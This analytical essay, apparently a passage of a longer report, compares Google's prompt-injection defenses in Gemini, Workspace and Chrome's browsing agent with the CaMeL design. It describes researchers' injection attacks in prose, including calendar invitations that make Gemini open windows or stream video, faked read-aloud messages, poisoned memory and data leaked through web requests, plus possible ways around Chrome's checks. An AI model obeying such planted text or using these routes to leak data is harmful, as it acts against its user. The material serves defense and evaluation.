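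### The missing rate for the whole system

*Mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Google's June 2025 post on its product defenses, says that adversarial training significantly strengthened Gemini 2.5 and describes the layers Google has added around the model. It doesn't report how often an attack gets past all of them.

Google measures how simulated attacks on Workspace perform with and without each defense, but Gavish's April 2026 post doesn't include those measurements. The post says a new workflow increased the generation of synthetic attack data by 75 percent. This could help Google update its defenses faster, but it doesn't measure how well they work.

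Rates for separate layers can't fill the gap, because an attack that gets past one layer may be unusually good at getting past the next. Suppose that a harmful action requires three things to happen: a classifier misses the injection, Gemini follows it and the user approves the action. The chance of success is

`P(success) = P(missed) × P(followed | missed) × P(approved | missed and followed)`

The vertical bar means "given that". Suppose a classifier misses 10 percent of a set of test attacks and a model follows 50 percent of the same set. If the two failures were independent, 5 percent of the attacks would get past both. But the attacks the classifier misses might be the best-disguised ones. If the model followed 90 percent of those, 9 percent of the full set would get past both. An adaptive attacker could send only the kind of message the classifier misses. Nearly all of these would reach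 the model, which would follow about 90 percent of them.

Anthropic's browser results show that the layers around a model can also make a very large difference. Google's layers might help Gemini as much, but Anthropic used different safeguards, models and test environments, so its results can't replace the missing figure for Gemini.

User confirmation is especially hard to include in such a figure. Testers who count every confirmation request as a stopped attack are assuming that users always notice when something is wrong, while those who count every request as approved give the confirmation layer no credit. For a realistic estimate, people would need to use the assistant for ordinary work, approving many legitimate actions and occasionally encountering a malicious one. Gavish doesn't explain how Google's simulations handle these requests.

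## How have Gemini's defenses fared against outside researchers?

In its published tests, Google attacked the model without the layers that surround it in a product, while outside researchers attack the product itself from ordinary accounts. Between February and August 2025, these researchers reported several ways planted text could make Gemini act against its user. Google says it has dealt with all of them, but one of the later attacks worked despite defenses Google had added after the first report.

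### Calendar invitations

In *Invitation Is All You Need*, Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025) attacked the Gemini web and mobile apps and a Gemini-powered version of Google Assistant. Their attacker needs only the victim's email address. The attacker plants instructions in an email, a calendar invitation or a shared document, then waits for the victim to ask Gemini about their mail, schedule or files.

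The paper describes 14 attack scenarios in five classes. The researchers carried out 11 of them on their own accounts. They inferred two more, phishing and a self-spreading worm, from attacks that had worked. For the last, disinformation planted in Gemini's memory, they cited another researcher's earlier demonstration.

| Threat class | Scenarios and the researchers' risk ratings |
|---|---|
| Short-term context poisoning, which changes Gemini's answers in one conversation | Phishing (very high), abusive text (high), spam (medium) |
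| Long-term memory poisoning, which affects later conversations | Disinformation (low) |
| Tool misuse, which turns a service's own tools against the user | Deleting or adding calendar events (medium) |
| Automatic agent invocation, which reaches a different Google service | Opening the windows at home (critical), switching on the boiler (high), controlling the lights (high) |
| Automatic app invocation, which opens another app on the phone | Streaming the user's video through Zoom (critical), stealing emails (critical), a worm (critical), stealing meeting details (very high), locating the user (high), downloading a file (medium) |

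Ten of the 14 scenarios (71 percent) are rated high or above. The paper gives 73 percent, apparently because it counts the Zoom attack twice, once for invitations and once for email.

Each rating combines impact with likelihood, using a method adapted from a car security standard. The researchers call nearly all of the attacks "very likely", which describes how easy they are to attempt. The likelihood score averages six factors, none of which is a measured success rate: the equipment, skill, knowledge and preparation time an attacker needs, how often the opportunity arises, and how much the victim has to do. The impact scores can also go beyond what the researchers demonstrated. They rate email theft as critical because emails are sensitive, but their demonstration extracted only the subject of an email.

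The researchers reported the attacks on February 22, 2025, and Google asked for 90 days to respond. In a statement printed in the paper, Google says it required confirmation for more actions, improved its link checks and deployed a classifier to filter out malicious instructions. It then reran the researchers' attacks, with variations, to check the fixes. Google calls the techniques "theoretical" in the statement, although the researchers had sent it videos of the attacks working.

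Nassi and colleagues write that the layers Google described in June 2025 were either ineffective or not yet deployed at the time of their study. Their results therefore show what could happen to Gemini users in early 2025, but not how well the finished set of defenses works.

### Messages read aloud

A follow-up study, SafeBreach's *Gemini's Secret Affair* (2026), comes closer to such a test. Or Yair, who co-wrote the invitation study, wanted to know whether Google's new defenses would hold. The study reports that Gemini refused every time he tried an earlier technique for triggering actions, which is independent evidence that Google's changes had worked against that technique. He then found another way to trigger actions.

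The new attacks targeted Gemini's voice assistant on Android, which can read notifications aloud. Anyone who could message the victim through WhatsApp, Slack, SMS or a similar app could supply the planted text. Yair again opened connected windows and started a Zoom video stream, although the Zoom demonstration used a phone configured to redirect a real web address to a test server.

In one of the two new harms, Gemini read out a fake message that appeared to come from the victim's manager, asking the victim to upload research documents to a Drive folder. The attacker didn't need to know a contact's name in advance, because Gemini could attribute the fake message to someone who had really written to the victim. People often use the voice assistant while driving, when they can't easily check the screen.

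The other new harm lasted beyond the conversation. Yair made Gemini save a false name for the user in its long-term memory and schedule a task to read the user's recent messages every day at 8 p.m. That memory belongs to the user's account, and Kaspersky's *Attacks on Gemini* warns that a message to someone's phone could therefore affect an agent that handles their work email on another device.

SafeBreach gives the attacks no formal risk rating and, according to The Hacker News (2026), lists no CVE (an entry in the public catalog of software vulnerabilities). Yair reported the attacks on August 17, 2025, and Google confirmed on November 14 that improvements to its content classifier had mitigated them. SafeBreach doesn't describe retesting the attacks itself.

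Google's tests of static and adaptive attacks suggest that a classifier can stop the reported attacks and still miss a new one. The invitation study had estimated that five measures together would reduce every risk to medium or lower, because an attacker would need a cluster of specialized processors, detailed knowledge of the defenses and months of preparation. Google deployed a different set of measures, so Yair's success doesn't directly disprove the estimate. But Yair studied the defenses by trial and error and reported the new attacks less than six months after the first disclosure.

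### Private information in a web request

Tenable, another security company, found that user data could leak through the tool Gemini uses to fetch web pages. According to Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool*, an injected instruction could make Gemini put the user's saved information and location in a web address and request that page from an attacker's server without asking for confirmation.

Tenable rated the flaw high severity, and Google rated it S2 on its own scale and paid a bounty. Tenable reported it on April 16, 2025. Google said on June 18 that the flaw was fixed, and Tenable confirmed the next day that the attack no longer worked.

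Tenable's *The Trifecta* reports that Google had already blocked the easier ways to leak data through images and links in Gemini's answers. Those checks didn't cover the browsing tool, which sends its request before Gemini displays anything.

Tenable also found two flaws in how Gemini takes in text. In Gemini Cloud Assist, which helps customers manage Google's cloud services, an attacker could plant text in a server log that made Gemini include a phishing link in its summary of the log. Google stopped displaying clickable links in those summaries. The other flaw, which Tenable's *Gemini Search Personalization Model* rates medium, let a malicious website add entries to a visitor's search history. Gemini read the history to personalize its answers and could follow instructions in it. Google withdrew the affected model.

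In January 2026, Security Boulevard's *Exploiting Google Gemini to Abuse Calendar Invites Illustrates AI Threats* (2026) covered another attack that used calendar invitations, found by the security company Miggo. SecurityWeek's *Weaponized Invite Enabled Calendar Data Theft via Google Gemini* explains that an invitation could make Gemini leak summaries of the victim's private meetings to the attacker by writing them into a new calendar event.

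### What a demonstration can show

Each of these demonstrations proves that planted text could cause a harmful result in a Google product at the time. They don't show how often an attack would succeed in ordinary use, because researchers look for a version that works and publish that one. Tenable mentions that Gemini recognized one of its attempts as suspicious, but Tenable, SafeBreach and the invitation study don't give success rates over a fixed number of trials.

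Researchers also have little reason to publish long accounts of attacks that Gemini stopped, so a list of disclosures can't show what share of attempts Google's defenses catch. It doesn't show that Gemini is less secure than a product that fewer people have examined, either.

### Analysis: would CaMeL have blocked these attacks?

The answers below are inferred from two parts of CaMeL's design: a planner that never sees untrusted text, and rules on where private data may go. They are not based on tests of these attacks against CaMeL.

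Gemini already had some isolation when Nassi and colleagues attacked it. One model, the orchestrator, planned the work and called separate agents for Calendar, Gmail, Google Home and other services. Each agent kept its context private, and only the orchestrator could start another agent. But unlike CaMeL's planner, the orchestrator received the agents' output, which could include an attacker's text.

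Suppose the user asks about this week's meetings. CaMeL's program might be:

```
events = read_calendar("this week")
show_user(events)
```

An event title can contain an instruction to open the windows, but this program has no step that controls the house. The same reasoning applies to the other harms in the table, assuming the user asked Gemini only to read or summarize something.

| Harm shown | Planner that never sees the text | Rule on where private data may go |
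|---|---|---|
| Opening windows or deleting a calendar event | Blocks it | Doesn't apply, since no data has to leave |
| Saving a false memory or scheduling a daily task | Blocks it | Doesn't apply |
| Streaming video through Zoom | Blocks it | Probably doesn't help, since Zoom sends the video itself |
| Locating the user by opening a web page | Blocks it | Doesn't help, since any connection reveals the device's network address |
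| Sending saved information or meeting titles in a web request | Blocks it | Blocks it |
| Copying private meetings into an event the attacker can read | Blocks it | Blocks it |
| Reading out a faked message | Doesn't block it | Doesn't apply |
| Showing a phishing link in a log summary | Doesn't block it | Doesn't block it without a further rule on links |

The fixed plan provides most of the protection here because the attacks depended on actions unrelated to the user's request. A data rule would matter more if, for example, the user asked Gemini to read an event page and open the booking site recommended there. The program would then have to fetch an address chosen by the page's author. If the quarantined model also had the user's saved information, it could hide some of that information in the address. CaMeL's tags would let a policy block that request, although a well-written program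 wouldn't give the quarantined model the saved information at all.

Actions that depend on a message are harder to protect. If a user says, "Open the gate when Dana texts that she's here", the program must include a step that opens the gate. Anyone who can send a text may be able to trigger it, unless the program or a policy checks the sender's number against the phone's contacts. A rule limiting where private data can go wouldn't help, because opening the gate doesn't disclose any private data.

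CaMeL's isolation also has to last for the whole conversation. After Gemini reads out the meetings, the user might say, "Move the second one to Friday." The planner then has to identify that meeting. Pasting the previous answer into its prompt would be simplest, but that would expose the planner to the invitation's title and reopen the route these attacks used. The interpreter could instead keep the events in a variable and show the planner only that a list of events exists.

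Nassi and colleagues propose a check that doesn't need a separate planner. The assistant would work out its response to a request twice, with and without the outside data, and ask the user to confirm if the outcomes differed. A command to open the windows would stand out when the user had asked only about meetings. But the assistant would also ask for confirmation when the user wanted the outside data to affect the action. To send Bob his document, the assistant has to get his address from the meeting notes, so the two outcomes would differ even if nobody had tampered with the notes.

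#### False text and mistaken trust

CaMeL doesn't guarantee true summaries, so the user would still hear that their manager wanted the research documents. Ordinary software could make the impersonation harder. A program could read out each sender's name, taken from the phone's own record, and then the unchanged message, instead of having a model summarize the notifications. The user would lose the convenience of a summary and might still be fooled by a message worded to sound as if a second one had begun.

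The phishing link in the log summary is easier to handle because a fixed rule can remove links, as Google's repair did. That rule is part of how the summary is displayed and would work the same with or without CaMeL.

The attack on Gemini's search history exposes a different weakness, because a search history appears to contain the user's own words. If CaMeL's developers had treated the history as trusted and given it to the planner for personalization, the attacker's entries could have influenced the plan. CaMeL would have blocked this attack only if its developers had realized that a website could write to the history.

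## How much of CaMeL has reached Chrome's Gemini agent?

Chrome's agent uses one idea from CaMeL by requiring a model that doesn't read web pages to approve each action. It doesn't have CaMeL's fixed plan or tags on individual values.

Google calls the agent auto browse. It clicks, types and moves between websites for the user, for example to fill in a form or put together a grocery order. Sood (2026) reports in *Android users just got one of Chrome's biggest Gemini upgrades* that it reached subscribers on Android phones in the United States in August 2026. Kanchwala (2026) reports in *Gemini Can Now Browse For You, But Should You Let It?* that subscribers in India can use it too, and Google Cloud offers it to eligible Workspace users in the United States.

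Auto browse works in the user's own browser, so it can reach sites where the user is signed in, such as webmail or a bank. An injected instruction could come from a malicious site, or from an advertisement or customer review on a legitimate one.

### A second model that checks each action

In the December 2025 post on Chrome's design, Parker says the *User Alignment Critic*, a separate model built with Gemini, was inspired partly by the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL. Berschadski also linked the critic to CaMeL in August 2026.

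Suppose a user asks the agent to buy a T-shirt, and a review on the shop's page contains an instruction to buy a gift card as well. The planner, which is the main Gemini model, reads the request and the page, including the review, and then proposes an action. Google has trained the planner on known attacks and uses spotlighting to mark the page as untrusted, but Parker still describes any model that reads web content as inherently vulnerable.

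The critic compares the planner's proposed action with the user's goal before the browser carries it out. The critic receives only metadata about the action, not the page. It should approve adding a T-shirt to the cart, in which case the browser clicks the button, but it should veto adding a gift card. After a veto, the critic sends feedback to the planner, which tries a different step. The planner can hand control back to the user after repeated failures.

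The critic is a more independent check than a classifier because it never receives the wording that misled the planner. It is still a Gemini model, so it could share some of the planner's mistakes about which actions fit a request.

How well the isolation works depends on which fields count as metadata, and Google hasn't published a list. A button's label, for example, comes from the web page, so if the critic receives it, whoever controls the page controls part of the critic's input. Without the label, the input may show only that the agent is about to click something on a certain site, which could be "Add to cart" or "Delete account". Parker writes that the critic receives no "unfiltered" web content and that the web can't poison it "directly". Neither statement rules out some page text reaching the critic in altered form, perhaps through the planner's description of an action.

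The feedback loop also gives an attacker more than one try, because the planner still has the injected text in its context after a veto. Google hasn't said how often the critic errs or how many vetoes it takes before the planner stops.

CaMeL's isolated model writes the plan, whereas Chrome's isolated model, the critic, only checks actions proposed by a planner that has already read the attacker's text. Chrome's agent lacks control-flow integrity because an attacker who takes over that planner can propose any action at any step, with only the critic and Chrome's other checks to block it.

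In return, the agent can adapt to surprises. If the T-shirt is out of stock, the planner can look at the page and suggest a similar one, and the critic can approve the unplanned step. The computer-use version of CaMeL could do this only if its program already had a branch for it. But the critic may also veto legitimate steps. For example, a form that asks for an unusual document could require a step that makes sense only to someone who has read the page, and the critic might block it.

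### Limiting the agent to certain sites

Browsers already keep websites apart with the *same-origin policy*. An *origin* is the protocol, host name and port in a web address. Under the policy, a malicious page can't read the user's bank page, even if both are open. An agent can undo this protection because it reads pages from both sites and can type information from one into the other.

Chrome's answer is *Agent Origin Sets*, which Parker presents as an extension of the browser's existing separation of sites, not as something taken from CaMeL. For each session, Chrome is meant to keep two sets:

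- **Read-only origins:** The agent may read content from these sites.
- **Read-writable origins:** The agent may also click and type on these sites.

If the user wants the ingredients for a recipe, the recipe site could be read-only and the grocery shop read-writable. A recipe comment might contain a hidden instruction to open the user's bank, but the bank is in neither the read-only nor the read-writable set.

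A *gating function* decides which of the planner's proposed sites are relevant to the task. Like the critic, it doesn't see web content. When the planner proposes opening a new site, a variant of the critic checks its relevance before Chrome adds it and loads the page. The same check applies when a page initiates the navigation itself. The planner can also use pages the user has explicitly shared, but it can't add a site without the gating function's approval.

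The sets also apply to frames, which are parts of a page that load from another site. On a shop's page, the agent would receive only the frames relevant to the task, so an instruction in a banner advertisement from an unlisted site would never reach the planner. For tools that don't involve web pages, Chrome separates calls that read from calls that write, and checks whether each suits the task.

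Writing `R` for the read-only set and `W` for the read-writable set, the full design lets data flow from site `a` to site `b` under this condition:

`a ∈ R ∪ W  and  b ∈ W`

The condition mentions sites but not the data, whereas CaMeL's policies apply to individual values.

The difference matters when a task involves a private site. Suppose a user asks the agent to buy the ingredients for a recipe that their sister emailed. The agent has to read the user's webmail and act on the grocery site, where an attacker has posted a review telling it to find a password reset code in the mail and post it as another review. Both sites belong to the task, so the origin sets allow the transfer. The critic may veto posting the review, and Chrome may ask the user first, but neither is certain. CaMeL would stop the attack at the planning stage because a program for buying ingredients has no step that posts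 a review. Even if the user had also asked for a review, a policy could keep text from the mailbox out of it.

#### Addresses written by the model

Chrome also has a deterministic check meant to stop the agent from leaking data through the URLs it opens. The check restricts model-written URLs to known, public ones, so it should block a URL that the planner has just built from a user's reset code.

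An attacker might still get data out one digit at a time by publishing a page for each digit and having the agent open the pages in the order of the code. Because every address would be known and public, the relevance check on new sites would have to stop the agent from visiting the attacker's site, and that check relies on a model.

### What the first version left out

Parker writes that Google first built a simpler version that tracked only the read-writable set, to see how the limits affected real tasks before adjusting them. With a single set, Chrome can restrict where the agent acts, but it has no separate list of sites that the agent may only read. A recipe site that the agent only needs to read would apparently need permission for clicking and typing too.

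An outside study shows why the missing set matters. In *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) tested seven browsers with AI assistants in January and February 2026. In their attack, a malicious page embeds a frame from a sensitive site, and the user asks the assistant to summarize the page. The page contains hidden instructions to include the frame's content in the summary and type the summary into a form, which sends it to the attacker. The attack works only if the sensitive site allows other pages to embed it, and many sites don't. A malicious advertisement can also use the attack to steal from the page around it.

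The researchers carried out the full theft only on OpenAI's ChatGPT Atlas. They found that Chrome with Gemini met the preconditions, so the theft could work there if an injection succeeded, but they didn't show one succeeding. The finding concerns Gemini in Chrome generally, so it may not apply to auto browse. But a list of writable sites wouldn't prevent this kind of theft, because the user has asked for help with the attacker's page and the agent may be allowed to type there. A working read-only set would prevent it by keeping the sensitive frame from the model.

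Google has published little about its progress since then. In January, Bawa wrote in *Q4 2025 Summary from Chrome Security* (2026) that the team hoped to share more as it rolled out the new mechanisms. *Q1 2026 Summary from Chrome Security* (Bawa, 2026), issued in April, reports that auto browse had launched and that the team was tuning the defenses based on real use, but it doesn't mention the read-only set. Berschadski's August post describes limiting the agent to relevant sites but doesn't distinguish reading from writing.

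#### What the browser's code enforces

Some evidence comes from Chromium (2025), the open-source project on which Google builds Chrome. Its code decides whether the agent may open a page roughly like this:

```
def may_open(current_page, destination):
    if company_has_rule_for(destination):
        return company_rule(destination)       # allow or block
    if google_has_rule_for(current_page, destination):
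        return google_rule(current_page, destination)
    if same_origin(current_page, destination):
        return Allow
    if is_sensitive(destination) and not user_confirmed(destination):
        return AskUser
    if already_allowed_in_task(destination):
        return Allow
    if confirm_new_sites:
        return ask_server(destination)
    return Allow
```

Everything before the last three lines is a list lookup or an address comparison. The request to the server is the point where a model could judge whether a new site is relevant. Chromium's defaults turn on the checks in general and the question about sensitive sites, but turn off `confirm_new_sites`, so the browser lets the agent open an unfamiliar site that isn't on any list without asking the server.

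This doesn't prove that auto browse users lack the relevance check. Google can change such settings remotely for some or all users, and its servers may vet an action before sending it to the browser. The code suggests that the browser relies on such vetting, because by default an action can add the site it needs to the allowed list. That would be safe only if something had already checked the action.

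Comments in Chromium's settings describe a "dark launch" mode, in which the browser checks a new site with the server and records the result but lets the agent continue regardless. Before enforcing the check, Google could use this mode to measure how often it would interrupt people. This mode is also off by default.

Chromium's code contains little sign of the read-only set. The metadata that Chromium attaches to a task includes newly added writable sites, but only for a page's main frame, not for embedded content. The file that defines the execution engine, the component that runs the agent's actions, mentions writable sites but no read-only ones. One screenshot method has an option to black out frames from other sites, but the method is off by default, and the option would hide those frames even if the task needed them. Chromium's code changes constantly and Google could enforce a read-only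 set on its servers, so the set may be in use without appearing in the code, but no public document shows that it is.

### The page classifier and confirmations

While the planner runs, a classifier checks every page the agent sees for injected instructions and blocks actions based on content it judges to be an attack. This is the same kind of defense as the classifiers in Workspace, and Parker acknowledges that it can't catch everything.

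Chrome also asks the user before the agent opens certain sensitive sites, such as those for banking or medical information, and before it signs in with a saved password. The model has no direct access to saved passwords. For purchases, payments and messages, the agent will "try to pause" and ask for permission or have the user complete the step. In Google's T-shirt example, the agent fills the cart and leaves the payment to the user.

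The agent lists its steps in a work log so that the user can stop it or take over. On a long task, the log may be too tedious to follow closely, but a confirmation request comes at the moment of risk.

### Fixed rules and model judgments

Chrome enforces a few of these protections entirely in software. It applies the lists of blocked and sensitive sites, keeps saved passwords away from the model and restricts the addresses the model may write. An attacker can't get around these rules by rewording an instruction, but can look for something they don't cover, such as a small clinic's patient portal missing from the list of sensitive sites.

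Chromium also checks the site again before an action that affects an open page, and the action fails if the page has moved to another origin while the check was running. This prevents a malicious page from being approved as one site and then switching to another just before the click.

The critic, the page classifier, the planner's training and spotlighting are all probabilistic. So is part of the confirmation layer, because Chrome, according to Parker, uses both fixed and model-based checks to decide when to ask the user. Comparing a site with a list is deterministic, but recognizing that a button on an unfamiliar site commits the user to a purchase may well take a model's judgment.

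With origin sets, software can reliably keep the agent off any site outside the set, but a model selects which sites go in. If the gating function wrongly accepts an attacker's site as relevant, the software will let the agent use it. CaMeL instead uses a written policy to decide whether to allow each action.

Business customers can add controls on the data itself. According to Berschadski, Chrome Enterprise Premium inspects the agent's data transfers and can block some that involve financial or personal information. The agent also can't open or export data that the employee isn't authorized to use. These controls could stop some leaks between two permitted sites. They don't limit the agent to the data a task needs, since employees usually have access to much more.

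Google tests the defenses together using automated attacks from malicious websites, focusing on advertisements, social media posts and other routes that could reach many people. It checks each change to the defenses against the attack success rate, which it hasn't published. It also pays outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating a serious breach of the agent's security boundaries.

### CaMeL, Workspace and Chrome compared

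The Workspace column covers Gemini's general protections, including its rules on tool chaining, and not the separate controls in Workspace Studio.

| | CaMeL | Gemini in Workspace | Chrome's agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the planner sees | The user's request and tool descriptions, but no untrusted content | The request together with emails and files | The request and the web pages it visits |
| Who checks actions | An interpreter that applies written policies | A policy engine, and the user for some actions | The critic, fixed rules in the browser, and the user for some actions |
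| How it tracks data | By value, recording each value's source and permitted readers | By what the session has already accessed; Google describes no tracking of values | By site; the first version tracked only sites where the agent may act |
| When it asks the user | When a policy requires it, such as for an unfamiliar email address | Before certain risky actions | Before it opens listed sensitive sites or uses saved passwords; it also tries to ask before purchases, payments and messages |
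| What it guarantees | The agent takes no action outside its plan; protection of data depends on correct policies and tags | Fixed rules hold, such as not loading external images, but injected text can still influence the plan | Fixed rules hold, such as the block on listed sites, but injected text can still influence the plan |

Suppose a user asks Chrome's agent to send Bob his document, where the meeting notes are a web document and the agent sends the email through the user's webmail. If an attacker has added an instruction to the notes to forward the inbox, the planner may follow it. The critic would probably stop the action, because forwarding an inbox has nothing to do with sending Bob one document.

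If the attacker has only changed Bob's address in the notes, the critic has little evidence of an attack, because the user asked the agent to email Bob and the planner proposes an email. Even if the metadata includes the recipient's address, the critic can't read the notes to check where it came from, and the notes would contain the wrong address anyway. Origin sets don't help because the notes and the webmail are both relevant to the task. As in Workspace, the classifier finds no instruction to flag, so the only remaining defense is the confirmation before sending.

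Willison's 2023 dual-LLM pattern had the same weakness. CaMeL added tags and policies to address it, and Google hasn't described anything equivalent in Chrome. On this point, Chrome's agent is closer to Willison's proposal than to CaMeL, but it doesn't fully follow that proposal either, because its planner reads the web.

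## What does Google's own writing say about why CaMeL was not shipped whole?

Google's main papers and posts on agent security don't explain why the company hasn't shipped CaMeL as a whole, and none of them reports a decision against it. But Google staff have described CaMeL's limitations and what they want from a defense, which makes some explanations more plausible than others.

| Possible reason | What Google staff and their co-authors have written |
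|---|---|
| Policies are hard to write and maintain | CaMeL's authors call this a limitation of CaMeL |
| Users tire of approving actions | CaMeL's authors call this a limitation of CaMeL |
| Agents complete fewer tasks | The agent security paper makes this point about traditional controls in general |
| The design doesn't suit open-ended tasks | Two Google researchers note that CaMeL and similar systems assume policies set in advance |
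| It costs more to run | The posts on Chrome and Workspace don't mention it |
| Google had other priorities | No direct statement |

Google released the CaMeL code for researchers, not customers. According to SourcePulse's *camel-prompt-injection*, a summary of the code's public page, the code reproduces the paper's experiments, isn't a Google product and won't be maintained. That explains why Google couldn't just switch on the published version in Gemini, but not why it didn't build a version for Gemini.

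### Who writes the policies?

The CaMeL paper, in a passage that Willison quotes, says that prompt injection is still not solved. The first limitation it gives is that CaMeL "suffers from users needing to codify and specify security policies and maintain them". It adds that balancing security with a good user experience is hard, partly because of user fatigue.

Reducing one of these burdens increases the other, because users need more detailed policies if they want fewer questions.

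Willison has worked in application security for two decades and still hasn't fully figured out Amazon's cloud permission system. He is nervous about any design that makes ordinary users think about policies, and hopes for a version of CaMeL with well-chosen defaults and a clear interface.

In a consumer assistant, Google would have to write those defaults. Díaz and colleagues say that writing comprehensive policies is "complex and difficult to scale" when an agent can take a vast range of actions, but they are describing policy engines that Google uses, and they still recommend them. Workspace Studio also lets administrators write rules about data, although Quinney acknowledges that companies can struggle to put their written policies into practice.

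Google has shipped policies despite the work of writing them. That work better explains why CaMeL was not shipped whole in the Gemini app, where a private user has no administrator to write them, than in products Google sells to businesses.

The policy explanation also covers only half of the design, because CaMeL's fixed plan needs no policies. Google could have shipped the isolated planner and kept its existing confirmation requests for email and purchases. In banking tests by Garby and colleagues, CaMeL without policies completed about two-thirds of the tasks and still stopped nearly every attack. Something other than the policies must explain why Google didn't ship that version.

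Moving CaMeL to a new setting also takes work. *Evolution Under Fire* (2026) tests CaMeL on the *AgentDyn* benchmark but not on Agent-SafetyBench. The researchers couldn't fit CaMeL's interpreter and benchmark-specific policies into their general test setup without replacing the core of the defense. They did adapt Progent, another defense, in which a model writes a policy from each user request. Google controls its own software and would face fewer obstacles than outside testers, but its engineers would still have to document every tool's output for the planner.

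### Summarize and send

Díaz and colleagues argue that traditional security controls are not sensitive enough to context for versatile agents and "can overly restrict utility". In their example, an agent that reads a document and then sends an email may be sending a summary the user asked for or leaking private data, and a simple rule about those two steps treats both cases alike.

CaMeL is also deterministic, but it can often distinguish these cases because its plan comes from the user's request. The table compares it with a rule that blocks all email after the agent has read a document. The entries are inferred from the two designs, assuming a CaMeL policy that trusts any address the user typed.

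| User's request | Document | Simple rule | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Summarize it and send the summary to an address the user typed | Harmless | Blocks the email | Sends the email |
| Summarize it | Contains an instruction to email private data to an outsider | Blocks the email | Has no email step in its plan |
| Summarize it and send the summary to the address on the last page | Harmless | Blocks the email | Asks the user or blocks the email |
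| Summarize it and send the summary to the address on the last page | Contains an address the attacker has changed | Blocks the email | Asks the user or blocks the email |

CaMeL gets the first two cases right, while the simple rule blocks a legitimate email. Neither can distinguish the last two, because the address comes from the document. Summarize-and-send is therefore a good argument against simple rules but a weaker one against CaMeL. Kern co-wrote the CaMeL paper and the agent security paper, but the agent security paper doesn't mention CaMeL, so it's unclear whether Kern thought the objection applied to CaMeL.

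The broader concern about usefulness does apply to CaMeL, since agents running it completed far fewer AgentDojo tasks. Usefulness also affected how Google trained Gemini. Shi and colleagues write that their attack data went into Gemini's training because it didn't make the model worse at other tasks. As evidence, they cite a preview of Gemini 2.5 Flash that scored 1392 on a public leaderboard, level with other top models.

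That is the closest Google comes in these documents to stating a test for adding a defense to Gemini, and CaMeL would have had trouble passing it. The comparison isn't exact, because training data affects everyone who uses the model, whereas Google could have limited CaMeL to a few sensitive tasks. It is still a well-supported inference that Google didn't ship CaMeL whole because it would have made Gemini less useful, though Google hasn't given that reason.

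### Willison's objection to the hybrid approach

*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* stated that untrusted input must never be able to trigger a consequential action. In *An Introduction to Google’s Approach to AI Agent Security*, published the same month, Willison (2025) criticized Google's agent security paper because it "skirts around that issue".

Díaz and colleagues suggest that developers ask whether their agent can clearly distinguish a user's input from untrusted content. Willison objects that the only correct answer is no, so the question implies a solution that doesn't exist. He notes that Díaz and colleagues soon acknowledge this.

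The hybrid argument from Díaz and colleagues partly answers Willison. They let an agent keep its powers after it reads untrusted text, but a policy engine can take that into account when it checks a later action. For example, if the agent has just processed data from a known suspicious source, the engine might block emails to outsiders unless the user approves. Model-based defenses help with attacks that no rule anticipated, though Díaz and colleagues call these defenses "inadequate, on their own" where an application needs absolute guarantees.

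Willison likes the policy engine and compares its rule about suspicious sources to CaMeL's analysis of data flow. He is much less convinced by the model-based layer because he has trouble seeing what a defense without guarantees adds. One answer is that stopping most attacks leaves fewer for the user to catch. But the rule about suspicious sources works only if Google already suspects the source, so unlike the stricter standard, it wouldn't cover an attacker writing from an ordinary new account.

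The hybrid argument also doesn't explain why Google left out CaMeL's planner. CaMeL already combines fixed rules with a model's judgment, but it requires the model to plan before any untrusted text arrives. Google could have added classifiers and adversarial training to that design too.

In the abstract of the agent security paper, Díaz and colleagues call it an "aspirational framework" that reflects their current thinking. The paper gives principles for building agents and doesn't explain particular decisions about Gemini, so it may not have been meant to answer questions such as why CaMeL was not shipped whole.

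Google still gives developers similar advice. Help Net Security's *Google’s $10,000 refund test shows why AI agents need zero trust* quotes Google's Shubham Saboo and Eric Dong, who recommend letting the model handle "dynamic reasoning" while the infrastructure around it enforces strict limits. Those limits could, for example, block a $10,000 refund that someone had talked the agent into issuing. This approach leaves the planning to a model that may have read the attacker's text, and it relies on the surrounding software to limit the damage.

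### Isolating the policy instead of the plan

Tsai and Bagdasarian (2025), in *Contextual Agent Security*, come closest to a critique of CaMeL from within Google. They point out that CaMeL and similar systems assume predefined policies. They argue that a fixed policy can't anticipate every situation, so it will be too strict in some and too loose in others. Their own design, Conseca, writes a new policy for each request.

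When a user makes a request, a separate model writes rules for that task based on the request, the tool documentation and any other information the developer has chosen to trust, such as email addresses and file names. The main model then plans and acts as usual, reading whatever emails and documents it needs, while ordinary software checks each proposed action against the rules. If an action breaks a rule, the software blocks it and returns the reason, so the main model can try something else.

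In an example from Tsai and Bagdasarian, a user asks the agent to reply to urgent work emails. The rules let the agent send an email only if it comes from the user's account, goes to a work address and has "urgent" in the subject line. They don't let the agent delete anything.

Conseca keeps untrusted text away from the model that writes the policy, rather than the model that writes the plan, as CaMeL does. Tsai and Bagdasarian see two advantages in Conseca's approach: the planner has the full context, and developers have to change little in their existing agents. Both would matter to a company with agents already running in several products.

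Conseca also addresses a doubt Willison raised about the agent security paper, in which Díaz and colleagues say they want an agent's permissions to change with its task. Willison could imagine this only with another AI model setting the permissions, and he feared that injected text could influence that model. In Conseca, the model that sets the permissions doesn't read the emails and web pages where an attacker would plant such text, unless the developer has chosen to trust them.

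Tsai and Bagdasarian tested a prototype that used Gemini 1.5 Pro on 20 file and email tasks, with five trials.

| Policy | Average tasks completed, out of 20 |
|---|---|
| None | 14.0 |
| Fixed policy that allows everything except deletion | 12.2 |
| Conseca | 12.0 |
| Fixed policy that forbids any change | 0.0 |

They also planted an email telling the agent to forward messages about urgent security vulnerabilities to an employee. Without a policy, the agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to categorize emails. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except one, where the user had told the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails.

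Conseca was tested on different and far fewer tasks than CaMeL was on AgentDojo, so its seemingly small loss of two tasks is hard to compare with CaMeL's losses. Its security test was also much weaker, with one planted email compared with AgentDojo's hundreds of attacks.

In the example of Bob's document, Conseca would probably work well if Bob were already a contact, because the rules could list his address and the software would reject the attacker's. If Bob were a new client, the model that writes the rules wouldn't have his address, so it would have to allow email to anyone or block the task. Tsai and Bagdasarian illustrate this limitation with a request to carry out whatever tasks are in a manager's email. Because the model that writes the rules is protected from the email's contents, it can't determine which actions the task needs.

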